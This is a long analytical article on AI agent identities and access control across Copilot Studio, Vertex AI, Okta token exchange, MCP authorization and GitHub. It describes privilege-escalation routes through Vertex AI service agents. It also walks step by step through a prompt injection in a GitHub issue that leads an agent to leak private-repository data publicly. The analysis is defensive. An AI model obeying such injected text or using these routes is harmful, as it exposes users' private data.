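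The block took much longer to release than Microsoft first announced. At its Build conference in 2025, Microsoft (2025) listed "enforced end-user authentication" among its preview features, apparently an early name for the same control. An administrator notice republished by itelio then scheduled a preview for early August and general availability for the fall. On 8 October a further notice set the date at 30 October 2025, according to PUPUWEB's *Block the use of maker-provided credentials for authentication* (2025). That release was evidently delayed, because Microsoft's release plan for April to September 2026 listed a public preview since 3 September 2025 but still scheduled general availability for August 2026. A newer notice, also republished by itelio, gave the date as 25 August 2026.

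Microsoft may not have met this date either. The Microsoft 365 Roadmap entry *Block the use of maker-provided credentials for authentication* (2026), published on 2 July, listed the control as "in development". Microsoft's instructions for the control carry no preview warning, which suggests that it has left preview, but they give no release date. Administrators have had the preview version since September 2025, but Microsoft says preview features aren't meant for production use, and it recommends the block for production agents, among others.

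A second control, according to itelio's copy of the announcement, stops makers from sharing agents and flows that rely on maker or system credentials not intended for reuse. Microsoft scheduled a public preview for 24 July 2026, and its release plan lists general availability for September. The control could suit a company that wants makers to use their own credentials in private agents but not in shared ones.

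### Work with no user present

Copilot Studio uses event triggers to start work that no user has requested, such as a nightly search for duplicate payments. When a file arrives, a table changes or a set time passes, the trigger sends the agent a message about the event, and the model chooses which tools to call. Microsoft's *Event trigger overview* says that triggers can use only the maker's credentials, and that an agent can run on its own only if every tool that needs a login also has working maker credentials.

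Blocking maker credentials therefore breaks these agents, because each tool call then requires someone to sign in and nobody is there to do so at night. Microsoft's documentation states that agents that start on a schedule or run in the background will fail as a result.

Leaving maker credentials on also creates a risk during attended use. If the clerk's agent checks payments at night and answers employees during the day, the credentials it needs to check payments may also be available when it answers employees. Microsoft's *Add an event trigger* says makers see a warning about this before they publish such an agent.

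A trigger can also let outsiders reach the agent. Reshmee's example is a holiday-planning agent that receives and answers questions by email. The sender is in effect the requesting user, but has not logged in to the agent. An email with an injected instruction would reach a model whose tools use the maker's credentials.

A company has four main options for unattended work.

| Option | Account used in the connected system | What the company gives up |
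|---|---|---|
| Keep maker credentials | The maker's | Limits based on who is asking, and independence from the maker's job |
| Give the agent its own account | The agent's | Limits based on who is asking |
| Have users authorize the agent in advance | Each user's | The user's presence when the agent acts |
| Wait for a user to sign in | The user's | Unattended operation |

An agent that keeps maker credentials is safest if it is used only for unattended work. The block on these credentials applies to whole environments, so a company can allow them in one environment for unattended agents and block them in another for agents that employees share. The unattended agents still have the maker's access, so outside text that reaches them remains a danger.

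With the second option, the agent doesn't depend on the maker staying in their job. Copilot Studio can create an identity for each new agent in Microsoft Entra, Microsoft's login service, and deletes it with the agent. ITWeb dates the automatic creation of these identities to May 2026. Administrators can see which connectors the agent may call and set conditions on their use. But these permissions apply only in the Power Platform software that runs connectors. They can block an agent from using the payroll connector, but they don't control which of the 500 records the payroll system returns.

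Some agents can also have their own Microsoft 365 account and a place in the organization chart, according to Microsoft's *Where do I govern my Copilot Studio agents?*. How access works depends on whether an agent uses its Entra identity, acts for a user or logs in with its own account, according to the post, and permissions that suit an agent's first task may become excessive as it gains new connections. An agent's own account is another service account, and its permissions are excessive for some users because it serves people whose permissions differ, although a company can at least choose the account's permissions to fit the task.

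Under the third option, users give the agent access to their accounts before an event triggers it. D365 Hub's *Configure triggers with end user credentials for seamless event driven automation* reproduces a notice with a planned date of 2 June 2025 for this feature, which would let each user supply credentials for a shared agent. In September 2025, Microsoft moved the feature to a later release and, according to itelio, scheduled a public preview for 30 July 2026. Microsoft 365 Roadmap's *Share Autonomous Agents to End Users (Run-Only)* (2026) lists general availability of the related sharing feature for January 2027.

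This keeps each run within one user's permissions, which is enough for sorting her email or preparing her for meetings. But the agent can't find duplicate payments across all 500 employees unless the user who authorizes it can read every record. The user also has to consent before she knows what the triggering message will contain, and she won't be there to notice if the agent follows an instruction in it.

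These triggers may not work where an administrator has blocked maker credentials. They appear to meet the requirement for end-user credentials, but Microsoft still says in its instructions for the block that every trigger must involve an active user, and it mentions no exception. A company that wants both the triggers and the block should test them together before relying on the agent overnight.

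## A platform's default service identity: Google Vertex AI

On Vertex AI, Google's cloud platform for building and running AI models and agents, a developer can deploy an agent without choosing an account for it, because the platform supplies one. The maker of a Copilot Studio agent, by contrast, decides to sign in with her own account. In early 2026, two security companies showed that the accounts Vertex AI supplies had access to far more than the agents needed, and that employees with few permissions of their own could take over those accounts.

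### An account that Google creates

Google Cloud customers divide the computing and storage they rent into projects. A project can contain databases, running programs, and buckets, which hold files. Google's Identity and Access Management system (IAM) records what each identity is allowed to do with these resources.

Google Cloud customers can create and manage their own service accounts. Google also creates and manages accounts called service agents, which let its services work on a customer's resources. (A service agent is an account and contains no AI.) The logging service, for example, uses one to write logs to a customer's bucket. Google grants many service agents their roles automatically. Service agents don't appear in a project's list of service accounts, and the IAM page shows them only if an administrator ticks a box. An administrator could therefore review every account the page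 shows by default and overlook the one her AI agents use.

A cloud platform attaches a service account to the machine that runs a program, and an internal metadata service gives the program an access token for that account, so the program doesn't need to store a password. This is safer than writing a long-lived key into the code, where a thief could copy it. But other code on the same machine can also request the token, and it gets the same token whatever its purpose.

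According to Google Cloud's *Managing access for deployed agents*, an agent that runs under a service account can reach everything the account can. The agent's tools share that access, so if a developer writes a tool that opens only the staff handbook, the tool's own code is all that prevents it from opening other files the account can reach.

### What the default account could read

In March 2026, researchers at Unit 42 disclosed how much the default account could access (The Hacker News, 2026). Unit 42 belongs to Palo Alto Networks, which sells security products for clouds and AI agents. *Double Agents* describes how the researchers built an agent with Google's Agent Development Kit and deployed it on Agent Engine, the part of Vertex AI that hosts agents. They wrote one of its tools to reveal the credentials of the agent's own account. The test measured what hostile code could do once it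 was running inside an agent, since the researchers did not break into anyone else's agent or trick a model with injected text.

The account was the Reasoning Engine Service Agent, which Google attaches by default. The researchers could use its credentials to list and read the files in every storage bucket in the customer's project. The storage permissions that Unit 42 lists don't include permission to change or delete files.

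Suppose the payroll company keeps 20 buckets in one project, including one for staff handbooks and one for payroll exports. It deploys an agent to answer questions about the handbooks. The agent needs only the handbook bucket, but hostile code running in the agent could read all 20.

Unit 42 suggests that an attacker could deliver such code in a ready-made agent disguised as a productivity tool. That is plausible, although the post describes no victim. A careless developer could also expose the payroll exports without hostile code, by writing a tool that opens any file the model names. The agent would then be a confused deputy for any employee who asked for them.

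Unit 42 also used the same credentials to download core Agent Engine software packages from Google's private repositories, which an ordinary customer account could not open. Like Hardy's compiler, the service agent had authority from two sources. It could read the customer's files and Google's software, and code supplied by a customer could use both kinds of access. Google told Unit 42 that other controls prevent the service agent from altering production software, so the researchers could read these packages but could not have used them to tamper with other customers' agents.

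### From viewer to administrator

Unit 42 started with the ability to deploy an agent. Two months earlier, Shparaga and Hasson (2026) had examined in *Double Agent* how little access an insider needs to take over a service agent, and found two attack routes. They work for XM Cyber, which sells software for finding such routes.

The first route also went through Agent Engine. Someone with permission to update an existing agent could put their own code in one of its tools and obtain the credentials of the Reasoning Engine Service Agent. Even if they previously had no access to the company's storage buckets, they could then read all of them. They could also read the agents' chat sessions and stored memories, which may contain whatever employees have typed to the agents.

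The second route went through Ray, a library that spreads large computations over many machines, and involved no AI agent. Vertex AI can run Ray, and it attaches another service agent to the main machine of each Ray cluster. Shparaga and Hasson found that a user with the read-only role "Vertex AI Viewer" could open a command shell on that machine with full administrative rights. From there the user could obtain the service agent's token and read and write data in the project's storage buckets and in BigQuery, Google's data warehouse.

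XM Cyber reports that Google said the services were "working as intended" but forwarded the report to its product team to decide whether a fix was needed. Google's answer is easier to defend for the first route, because a person who can replace a program's code can usually make it do anything its account allows. Permission to update an agent is therefore in effect permission to use the agent's identity, and an administrator only has to know this before granting it. The answer is hard to defend for the second route, because an administrator who assigns a role called Viewer would not expect its holder to gain administrative rights on a machine.

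### Scopes and permissions

Unit 42 also warned about Google Workspace, which includes Gmail, Calendar and Drive. The deployed agent's token carried OAuth scopes for all three, and customers could not edit those scopes. Unit 42 did not find that this let any agent read a customer's email.

A Google token has to pass two checks. Its scopes determine which Google services will accept it, and IAM permissions then determine what the account may do to a particular resource. The agent's token had the scopes for Workspace, but its account lacked the necessary permissions by default. Unit 42 acknowledges that this is an effective boundary, but is concerned that the permissions were the only check restricting access to Workspace. If an administrator later gave the account access to Workspace data, the token's scopes would not limit what the agent did with it.

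In XM Cyber's Ray test, the Ray service agent had permission to create tokens for other service accounts, which might have let an attacker move on to still more powerful accounts. But Google refused the operation because the agent's token did not have the required scope.

| Account and action | Scope | Permission | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent's account reads the project's buckets | Present | Present | Allowed |
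| Agent's account reads Workspace data | Present | Absent by default | Refused |
| Ray account changes data in BigQuery | Present | Present | Allowed |
| Ray account creates tokens for other accounts | Absent | Present | Refused |

Neither check considers who is using the agent. Both apply to the account, so the result is the same for every requesting user.

### What Google has changed

Google responded to Unit 42 by revising its documentation to explain how Vertex AI uses accounts and resources, and by recommending that customers replace the default account with one of their own. A documentation change removes no permissions, so SecurityWeek's *Google Addresses Vertex Security Issues After Researchers Weaponize AI Agents* overstates the fix when it describes the issue as addressed. Unit 42 says Google also changed the deployment process, so the code in its post may no longer work, but it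 doesn't claim that the default account lost any access.

The larger change came on 22 April 2026, when Google renamed Vertex AI to Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform and Agent Engine to Agent Runtime. According to Google Cloud's *Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform release notes* (2026), Google also made Agent Identity generally available that day. Agent Identity gives each agent its own identity instead of an account that many agents share.

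A new agent identity can write logs, call models, and use its own sessions, memories and sandboxes (isolated spaces for running code). It has no access to the project's buckets until someone grants it. Google also ties the agent's tokens to the environment where the agent runs, so a stolen token doesn't work elsewhere, as Google Cloud's *Use Agent Identity with Agent Runtime* explains. The narrow starting permissions matter more for Unit 42's scenario, because a hostile tool inside the agent could still use the token from there but, with only those permissions, couldn't read the project's buckets.

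Developers have to request an agent identity when they create the agent. Otherwise, the agent still runs under the Reasoning Engine Service Agent, according to Google Cloud's *Set up the environment*, although the same page recommends the new agent identity feature. Google's release notes from 31 March to 23 November 2026 record no change to this default, and none that narrows the account's role. A company that uses the default should check the role's current permissions in Google's IAM documentation.

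The default account becomes more dangerous as a project grows, because all agents that use it share its permissions. If an agent needs more access, Google's instructions allow an administrator to grant the account additional roles. Suppose the payroll company does this so that one agent can query the payroll table. Its handbook agent, which runs under the same account, can then query the table too, although nobody has changed that agent.

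### What a custom account can limit

Google suggested a custom service account to Unit 42 as the remedy. The customer creates the account, grants it only the permissions one agent needs, and specifies it when deploying the agent. The developer must also have permission to use that account before deploying an agent with it, a requirement that Google's setup instructions don't list for the default account.

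This works well for the handbook agent. Its account can read one bucket instead of 20, and every employee may read the handbooks anyway, so an attacker who took over the agent would get almost nothing that employees cannot already open.

Suppose the company deploys a second agent that answers employees' questions about payslips, and stores all 500 payslips in one bucket. The custom account again removes access to the other 19 buckets, but the agent can still read every payslip, whichever employee is asking, because the storage service checks only the agent's account. Any account that serves users with different rights has this kind of excess access. Unit 42 is right that a custom account grants "only the specific permissions" an agent needs, but this agent needs access to all 500 payslips.

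The company could create several accounts. In its guide to custom accounts for training models and serving predictions, Google Cloud suggests giving each user's jobs access only to a certain table or bucket. This separates users because each job belongs to one person. The company could similarly deploy one agent for payroll clerks and another for everyone else, each with its own account, but the second agent would still serve hundreds of people with different rights. Deploying one agent per employee would be too much work, and for the jobs covered in the guide, Google Cloud allows at most 20 custom accounts per project, region and service.

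Agent Identity has the same limit. It separates agents from one another, so the handbook agent can't read the payslip agent's sessions, but it doesn't separate the payslip agent's users from one another. Google offers a different method for separating users, in which the agent asks each user for consent and receives a token for that user's account.

### The case for a separate identity

Amazon Web Services (AWS), Google's competitor in cloud computing, advises against always running agents under the requesting user's account. In *AGENTSEC03-BP02 Separate agent and human user permission*, it tells customers to create a dedicated identity for each type of agent, with only the permissions its tasks require, and to block agents from assuming roles meant for people. AWS recommends enforcing the block with organization-wide rules as well as in each agent's own settings, so that one misconfigured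 agent can't acquire an administrator's role.

When an agent acts for a user, AWS's guidance recommends a form of delegation in which the token identifies both the agent and the user. The systems the agent calls can then apply the user's permissions, and the agent never holds the user's credentials. AWS sells a product that issues such tokens, Bedrock AgentCore, and much of the guidance explains how to use it.

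AWS's other main argument is that when an agent uses an employee's account, as with maker credentials in Copilot Studio, audit logs attribute the agent's actions to that employee. AWS also warns against sharing one service account among several agents, because the log then doesn't show which of them acted. *AI Agent Identity*, by the head of Zitadel, which sells login software, makes the same objection to borrowed employee accounts. It calls a dedicated account with broad permissions only a halfway solution, because the log shows the right agent but the agent can still do too much.

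| Identity that the agent uses | What the log shows | What an investigator may not learn |
|---|---|---|
| A service account shared by several agents | The shared account | Which agent acted, and for whom |
| The agent's own account | The agent | Who asked |
| The user's account | The user | Whether the user or the agent acted |
| The agent's own account, with the user named in the token | Both, if the system records them | Little about who was involved |

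Google acknowledges the first problem in its documentation, noting that it can be hard to tell from the logs whom a service agent was acting for. Some service agents now record the person who started the job, but many don't. With Agent Identity, the logs show both the agent and the user when the agent acts on a user's behalf, and only the agent otherwise. Since 27 May 2026, companies that choose to log prompts and answers also get a user ID with them. These records help an investigator find out who obtained a colleague's payslip, but they don't stop the agent from handing it over.

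A dedicated identity makes the most sense for unattended work, such as the nightly search for duplicate payments. It also makes sense where all users may see the same data, as with the handbooks, and where a fixed program releases only a narrow result, as Ritchie's did with the accounting file. In these cases the company can also shut down one agent without locking out an employee or stopping other agents.

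The case for the payslip agent is weak if the storage service checks only the agent's own account. Naming the employee in the token helps only if something outside the model checks whether she is allowed to access the requested payslip.

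## Tokens that name the user but exceed the user's rights: a salary-server test

In June 2026 Okta, which sells login and access-management software, published a test of an agent that answers employees' questions about pay. In one of two designs, an engineer's agent received a token that correctly named him as the person it was acting for, but let it read and change every salary in the company, although he was entitled to see only his own. Okta's *An AI agent is not a service app* (2026) blames the practice of registering agents as ordinary applications and recommends giving each agent its own identity, a product Okta sells. The tokens Okta printed suggest a narrower cause: the server issued the token without checking the request against the engineer's entitlements.

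### How one token becomes another

An agent usually can't reuse the token that a user gets by logging in. The intended recipient of that token is the application the user logged in to, and a salary server should refuse it. The agent needs a second token for the salary server and can get one through token exchange. The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many of the internet's technical standards, has standardized this as RFC 8693. Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, the text of that standard, define a single request and response. For an employee called Charlie, the exchange works like this:

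1. The agent sends Charlie's token to the authorization server as the `subject_token`, which identifies the person the request is for.
2. It may add an `actor_token`, which identifies the agent itself. It may also state where it wants to use the new token and which scopes it wants.
3. The authorization server validates the tokens and decides, under its own policy, whether to issue a new one and with which scopes.
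4. The agent presents the new token to the salary server.

The new token is often a signed list of fields. Decoded, one for Charlie's agent might read:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.acme.example",
  "aud": "https://salaries.acme.example",
  "exp": 1790000000,
  "scope": "Salary:Read:Self",
  "sub": "charlie",
  "act": { "sub": "pay-agent" }
}
```

The `iss` field identifies the issuer, `aud` (audience) identifies the intended recipient, and `exp` gives the expiry time. The subject, `sub`, is the person the agent acts for, and the actor, `act`, is whoever is using the token. This is delegation, because the token identifies both the agent and the person it acts for to the salary server. The server could, for example, accept a change of address from Charlie himself but refuse the same change from his agent.

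Without the `act` field, the token would be an impersonation token, and nothing in these fields would show the salary server that an agent was involved. Jones and colleagues describe the user and the agent in this case as "indistinguishable" within the rights the token covers. An exchange that supplies only a subject token can produce only an impersonation token. If the agent also supplies an actor token, the authorization server can put both identities in the new token, depending on its policy.

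Neither field determines how much the agent may do. RFC 8693 does not require the new token's scopes to be a subset of the old token's. It mentions a narrower token for a downstream service as one use of the exchange, and it suggests limited scopes and short lifetimes to reduce abuse, but it leaves the rules for granting scopes to each authorization server. The optional `may_act` field in Charlie's token can restrict who may act for him, but not what that actor may do. The standard therefore permits attenuation, in which authority can be narrowed but not widened as it is passed on, but does not guarantee it.

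### Three employees at a salary server

Okta's test used an MCP server for employee compensation with three scopes. `Salary:Read:Self` lets a person read their own pay, `Salary:Read:All` allows reading everyone's pay, including the chief executive's, and `Salary:Write` allows changes to anyone's pay. Okta assigned the scopes by group. Charlie, an engineer, was entitled only to `Salary:Read:Self`. Alice, who plans compensation, could read all salaries but not change them. Bob, the chief financial officer, had all three scopes.

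The testers built the same agent in two ways. In the service-app design, they registered it as a service app, in effect a service account, which exchanged the user's token for one that the salary server accepts. In the agent-identity design, the agent had its own entry in the company's directory. It obtained a signed assertion naming both the user and the agent, then presented it to the salary server's authorization server to get a token. For each user, the agent made three requests, each with one more scope than the last.

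| User | Scopes requested | Service-app design | Agent-identity design |
|---|---|---|---|
| Charlie | Read:Self | Granted | Granted |
| Charlie | Read:Self, Read:All | Granted beyond his entitlement | Refused |
| Charlie | Read:Self, Read:All, Write | Granted beyond his entitlement | Refused |
| Alice | Read:Self | Granted | Granted |
| Alice | Read:Self, Read:All | Granted | Granted |
| Alice | Read:Self, Read:All, Write | Granted beyond her entitlement | Refused |
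| Bob | Read:Self | Granted | Granted |
| Bob | Read:Self, Read:All | Granted | Granted |
| Bob | Read:Self, Read:All, Write | Granted | Granted |

The service-app design granted all nine requests, including three that exceeded the user's rights. The agent-identity design refused only those three. Bob, who was entitled to everything, was the control. The agent-identity design granted his requests, which showed that it did not simply refuse all requests for powerful scopes. Okta describes his results in prose but prints no tokens for him.

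The service-app token for Charlie's largest request included these fields (`scp` is Okta's name for the scopes):

```json
{
  "sub": "charlie@acme.example",
  "scp": ["Salary:Read:All", "Salary:Read:Self", "Salary:Write"]
}
```

Okta's token names Charlie as the subject and holds his user ID in another field, although Okta says that this design does not carry the user and that it "bypassed his identity entirely". The token has no actor field, so in the terms of RFC 8693 it is closer to impersonation than to delegation. The service app appears only as the client that requested the token. If the salary server logged only the subject, the agent's actions would appear in the log as Charlie's, as happens to makers in Copilot Studio, although he never had this access himself.

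The exchange also widened Charlie's authority. His login token carried two scopes, one for logging in and one for invoking the agent, but the exchange returned a token with all three salary scopes. A rule that the output token may contain only scopes from the input token would have prevented this, but it would also have stopped Charlie from reading his own pay, because his login token contained no salary scopes. The authorization server needed to look up what he was entitled to, and in the service-app design it didn't.

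Okta's evidence consists of tokens and error messages, so it shows what an authorization server will issue but not how often a language model would request too much access. Okta argues that a prompt injection in a document could turn a user's question about their own pay into a request to export every salary. In the service-app design, the authorization server would not block that request.

Okta describes the correct result as the intersection of what the user, the agent and the resource allow. The agent-identity design was stricter. When Charlie's agent requested Read:Self and Read:All, the intersection was Read:Self, but the server refused the whole request instead of issuing a token for the permitted scope. This is safe, but an agent that routinely requests both scopes could not tell Charlie his own salary.

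### Which check refused the request

According to Okta, only the identity model changed between the two designs. Readers can check this by following Charlie's refused request for Read:Self and Read:All through the printed tokens.

In the agent-identity design, Charlie's agent first asked the company's identity provider, the service where employees log in, for the signed assertion. The identity provider issued one that named Charlie as the subject and the agent as the actor, with both Read:Self and Read:All in its scope field. The agent had its own identity and every party was correctly named, but Read:All exceeded Charlie's rights. The salary server's authorization server rejected the request only at the next exchange, with the message "policy evaluation failed". Okta's commentary credits the resource server with recognizing the excess, but the salary server never received a token to examine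 because the authorization server had already refused the request.

The same authorization server had issued the over-broad token in the service-app design. Its address appears as the issuer of that token and as the audience of the assertion it later refused. It could identify Charlie in both runs, since it wrote his name into the token in one of them, and it evidently had rules about his entitlements that it applied in the other. So the two designs differed in the check as well as in the agent's identity, and Okta tested only two of the four combinations:

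| | Server checks the user's entitlement | Server does not check it |
|---|---|---|
| Agent registered as a service app | Not tested | Excess scopes granted |
| Agent has its own identity | Excess scopes refused | Not tested |

A token exchange that checked Charlie's groups would almost certainly have refused the excess scopes too. Jones and colleagues require the authorization server to return an error when a token it receives is unacceptable under its policy, and to report the granted scopes if they differ from those requested. The second requirement would make little sense if the server always had to grant everything. The other untested combination would probably have failed, because an authorization server that trusted the scopes in the signed assertion would have let Charlie's agent read every salary under its own identity.

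Okta says that its service-app design limits a request only by the app's own grants and that a company "cannot bind the agent to the user's entitlement" this way. That may be true of Okta's product, but it isn't true of RFC 8693, which leaves the decision to the server's policy. Okta does not publish the rules it configured, so readers cannot tell whether its software cannot apply a group check to this exchange or the testers left one out. Until that is known, Okta customers have good reason to avoid the service-app design. Customers of other suppliers should ask whether their token exchange checks the user's entitlements, and test it with an employee like Charlie.

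Another vendor's demonstration supports the view that the check matters more than how broad the agent's own permissions are. Red Hat's *When an AI agent acts on your behalf* describes a system in which a policy engine, a program that makes access decisions from written rules, compares the user's departments with the agent's. One agent has access to every department but gives its users no extra access. It can't open a personnel document for a user without personnel access, because the policy engine also checks the user's departments. Red Hat promotes its own platform in the post. Its agents also have separate identities, so the demonstration does not fill either empty cell in the table.

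Okta also says a separate identity helps with auditing and with shutting down a single agent. It argues that an identity issued by an agent platform is a poor substitute because it sits outside the directory where a company manages everyone else's access. These are reasonable arguments for the product, but the salary test does not measure any of them.

Okta also cites an incident at PocketOS, in which a coding agent used a long-lived credential it found in a file to delete a production database. Okta acknowledges that the path was different, since the agent used an existing token and no exchange took place. Limiting the agent to its user's rights would have prevented the deletion only if the user had no right to delete the database.

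### The identity provider's assertion

The assertion in Okta's test follows a draft standard co-written by Parecki, who works at Okta. The draft, *Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant* (Parecki, McGuinness and Campbell, 2026), describes how one application can get access to another through an identity provider that both already use for login. It calls the general pattern Cross-App Access and the assertion an ID-JAG, and its main example is a wiki that displays content from a chat service. Ordinarily the wiki would ask each user to approve the connection, without involving the identity provider. InfoQ (2026) reports that repeated approval prompts are a major complaint from companies that use MCP.

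With an ID-JAG, the company's administrators approve the connection in advance. For a pay agent, the procedure has four steps:

1. Charlie logs in through the identity provider, and the agent's application receives proof of his identity.
2. The application sends this proof to the identity provider in a token exchange and asks for an ID-JAG addressed to the salary server's authorization server. The identity provider must check that it issued the proof to this application, and then applies the administrators' policy to the requested scopes.
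3. The application presents the ID-JAG to the salary server's authorization server, which must confirm that the ID-JAG is addressed to it and that the right application is presenting it. It then decides under its own policy whether to issue an access token.
4. The application calls the salary server with the access token.

Two servers therefore decide on Charlie's scopes, and either may grant fewer than he requested. The draft requires the identity provider to evaluate a policy and write the granted scopes into the ID-JAG, but it doesn't specify what the policy must contain. In Okta's test, the identity provider's policy allowed Read:All, but the other server's policy blocked it.

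Because the work is divided this way, the people who run the identity provider may assume that the salary system will refuse anything excessive. Those who run the salary system may see a signed ID-JAG that lists Read:All and assume that someone has already checked it against Charlie's job. The draft gives them some reason to assume this, since it has the salary system's authorization server treat the ID-JAG as an input to its decision. A company that adopts the draft should decide which of the two servers holds the salary rules and test that server on its own.

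The draft also doesn't guarantee that the salary server will receive any information about the agent. The actor field is optional in an ID-JAG, and the draft explicitly leaves it to later documents to define how actor tokens are handled. Okta's assertion named the agent in that field and, nested inside it, the web application Charlie had used to reach the agent. Another supplier could follow the same draft and name only Charlie.

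ID-JAG also needs a shared identity provider. In a reply on the working group's mailing list, Aaron Parecki described it as a special case of a broader draft on passing identity between organizations, and as an optimization for applications that use the same provider. If the payroll company's agent had to query a supplier with a different identity provider, the two companies would need the broader draft. That draft does not specify why the receiving side should trust the sender's assertions, so the companies would have to settle this themselves.

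### What the MCP rules require

The MCP specification of 28 July 2026 deals mainly with a different error, the use of a token at the wrong server. If the token that Charlie's agent uses for the staff-handbook server also worked at the salary server, anyone who controlled the handbook server could use it to collect his pay records. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), like Model Context Protocol (2025), requires a client to state the address of the intended MCP server in a `resource` parameter whenever it requests authorization or a token. The client must send the parameter even if the authorization server doesn't support it, in which case the token might not be tied to one server. The MCP server therefore still needs to check that the token was issued for it.

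Charlie's over-broad token would apparently have passed this test. The proper authorization server had issued it, its audience was the finance resource, and it had not expired. Checking the audience prevents a token for one server from working at another, but it doesn't detect a token that grants too much access at its intended server.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) bans the salary server from forwarding Charlie's token to the payroll database, but the server can still log in there with a service account. MCP's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires a separate token for the backend system but does not require that token to name Charlie. RFC 8693 offers a way to preserve his identity: a server can exchange a user's token it has received for one meant for a backend system. In the standard's example, the new token is valid for one minute. If the salary server makes this exchange,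 the payroll database can apply Charlie's own row permissions.

The specification's rules on scopes make the authorization server's decision even more important. When a client calls a tool without the necessary scopes, the MCP server should refuse and list the scopes that the call needs. A client acting for a user should then request a new token that adds them. Suppose Charlie's agent reads a document containing an injected instruction to export all salaries. The model calls the export tool, the salary server responds that the call requires Read:All, and the client requests that scope. With an interactive login, Charlie might see a prompt and wonder why. A token exchange or an ID-JAG can happen without a prompt, so the authorization server has to check whether he is entitled to the scope.

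The salary server has to interpret even a correct scope. `Salary:Read:Self` does not contain an employee's name, so the server must combine it with the token's subject and return only that person's record. If the server lets the model supply the name and checks only that the token has some read scope, Charlie's agent can retrieve his colleague's pay with a correctly issued token. The specification allows a server to determine the required scopes from a call's arguments but does not require this.

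MCP servers have a general duty to keep data from unauthorized parties, and the specification mostly leaves them to decide how. The Agentic AI Foundation, which oversees MCP, divides the work similarly. The authorization server identifies the user and issues the token, while the MCP server validates the token, checks its audience, and enforces scopes and its own policy. A salary server with such a policy could have looked up Charlie, found that he was an engineer, and refused to show him other people's pay despite the token. That check would have been a third place to catch the error, and the only one that works after the authorization server has made a mistake.

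These rules cover only connections over HTTP. Under the specification, a server that runs on the user's own machine and communicates directly with the client should instead take credentials from the local environment. A developer who starts a salary server on her laptop with a service-account key in its settings gets neither the audience check nor a token that names her.

MCP has also adopted ID-JAG as an optional extension. Model Context Protocol's *Enterprise-Managed Authorization* describes it as a way for a company to control access to MCP servers in one place. The Agentic AI Foundation calls the extension stable and suggests that an employee's access could change when they transfer, are promoted or leave. But clients must support the extension explicitly, and it is never on by default. It is useful only if the identity provider, the client and the MCP server's authorization server all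 work together, so Model Context Protocol has set up a group to test combinations of products.

To solve Charlie's case, the company would have needed rules for individual scopes, in addition to approving or blocking whole servers. InfoQ describes employees as inheriting access to the servers their organization has approved, and the salary server would have to be approved for everyone because all employees may see their own pay.

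### Fields without a settled meaning

RFC 8693 is a published standard, but the documents that adapt it to agents are drafts that are still changing. One is the ID-JAG draft by Parecki and colleagues, which the IETF's OAuth working group has adopted as a work item. The current version is dated 21 May 2026. Internet-Drafts lapse after six months, so it will expire on 22 November 2026 unless a newer version replaces it.

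*OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) is a separate April draft that expires on 1 November. McGuinness, who also helped write the ID-JAG draft, argues that existing standards provide the actor field but no consistent way to use it across token types or to mark whether an actor is a person, an application or an agent. Okta's assertion marks agents by setting a field called `sub_profile` to `ai_agent`, but RFC 8693 does not define that field. If the payroll company bans agents from changing salaries, a salary server from another supplier might therefore ignore the field and accept the change.

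The fields are easy to mix up. Red Hat's demonstration cites RFC 8693 as the pattern for its tokens, but puts the agent in `sub` and the user, Alice, in `act`, which is the reverse of the standard. A salary server that followed the standard would treat the agent as the employee whose pay it should look up. When one agent passes a request to another, Red Hat's tokens move Alice a level deeper, to a position that RFC 8693 reserves for earlier actors. The standard forbids recipients to consider earlier actors when deciding on access, so a compliant recipient would have to ignore Alice, whose permissions should limit the request. Red Hat's own policy engine considers every level, so the demonstration works as intended, but only with recipients that interpret the tokens the same way.

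### Limits for a user who may do everything

In Okta's test, checking the user's entitlement did not restrict Bob, the chief financial officer. Both designs gave his agent permission to change any salary. Okta calls this "the system working", which is accurate for a control case. In real use, however, Bob's agent is the most valuable one to attack, because his entitlement would cover an injected instruction to raise someone's pay.

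Every refusal in the test resulted from a limit on the user. Okta says its agent-identity design also limits the agent itself, as WorkOS proposes, but the test did not cover this because the agent had to be allowed all three scopes for Bob to receive them.

Red Hat's demonstration did test a limit on the agent. One user could open three of five documents directly: a financial report, a set of administrative policies, and a summary open to everyone. When he used an agent whose permissions covered finance and engineering, he could open only the financial report and the public summary, because the agent had no access to administrative documents and he had none to engineering. Red Hat's policy engine also denies access to any agent that isn't acting for a user, which would rule out unattended jobs such as the nightly search for duplicate payments.

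If the payroll company applied this to Bob, it could give his everyday agent the two reading scopes and require him to change salaries in the payroll system himself. An injected instruction then couldn't change anyone's pay through the agent, but it could still leak every salary if the agent had a way to send them out.

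## An agent with the user's own access: GitHub repositories

GitHub, where developers store and discuss code, gives an agent an easy way to send data out. Each project has a repository, which its owner makes public or private. Anyone with an account can normally open an issue, such as a bug report, in a public repository, and anyone on the internet can read what people post there. An agent using its user's account can therefore copy text from a private repository to a public page without exceeding the user's permissions.

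### From a private repository to a public page

In May 2025 Invariant Labs, a company that sells security tools for agents, demonstrated such a leak. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes a user who connects Claude Desktop, Anthropic's chat application, to GitHub through GitHub's official MCP server. The server works on the user's own account, as heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains, so the agent can open his private repositories as well as his public ones. The demonstration account owned a public repository with a simple Pacman game and several private repositories. The data moved as follows:

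1. An outsider opens an issue in the Pacman repository. The text, part of which appears in Willison, in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, complains that the project's author is not widely recognized. As a remedy, it asks for someone to read the README (the introductory file) of all the author's repositories and write about him.
2. The owner asks the agent to look at the open issues.
3. The agent fetches them, and the outsider's text enters the model's context.
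4. The model follows the instruction and reads the private repositories under the owner's account.
5. It opens a pull request, a proposed change to the code, in the Pacman repository and includes what it found.
6. The outsider reads the pull request, as anyone can.

The pull request revealed the names of private repositories, the owner's plan to move to South America and his salary. The model was Claude 4 Opus, then new. Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call by default, but Invariant Labs says many users choose "Always Allow". It gives no figures for how many do so or how often the attack succeeds.

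The outsider's text steered the agent as the customer's support ticket did in the Supabase demonstration, but here no role was exempt from the access rules and no one shared an account. Invariant Labs calls its finding a critical vulnerability in the GitHub MCP server, but also says that the server's code has no flaw and that GitHub could not solve the problem with a server patch. The second description is more accurate, because the server carried out requests that the account's owner was entitled to make.

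### Five correct decisions

An auditor who replayed the demonstration would find that GitHub had decided every request correctly.

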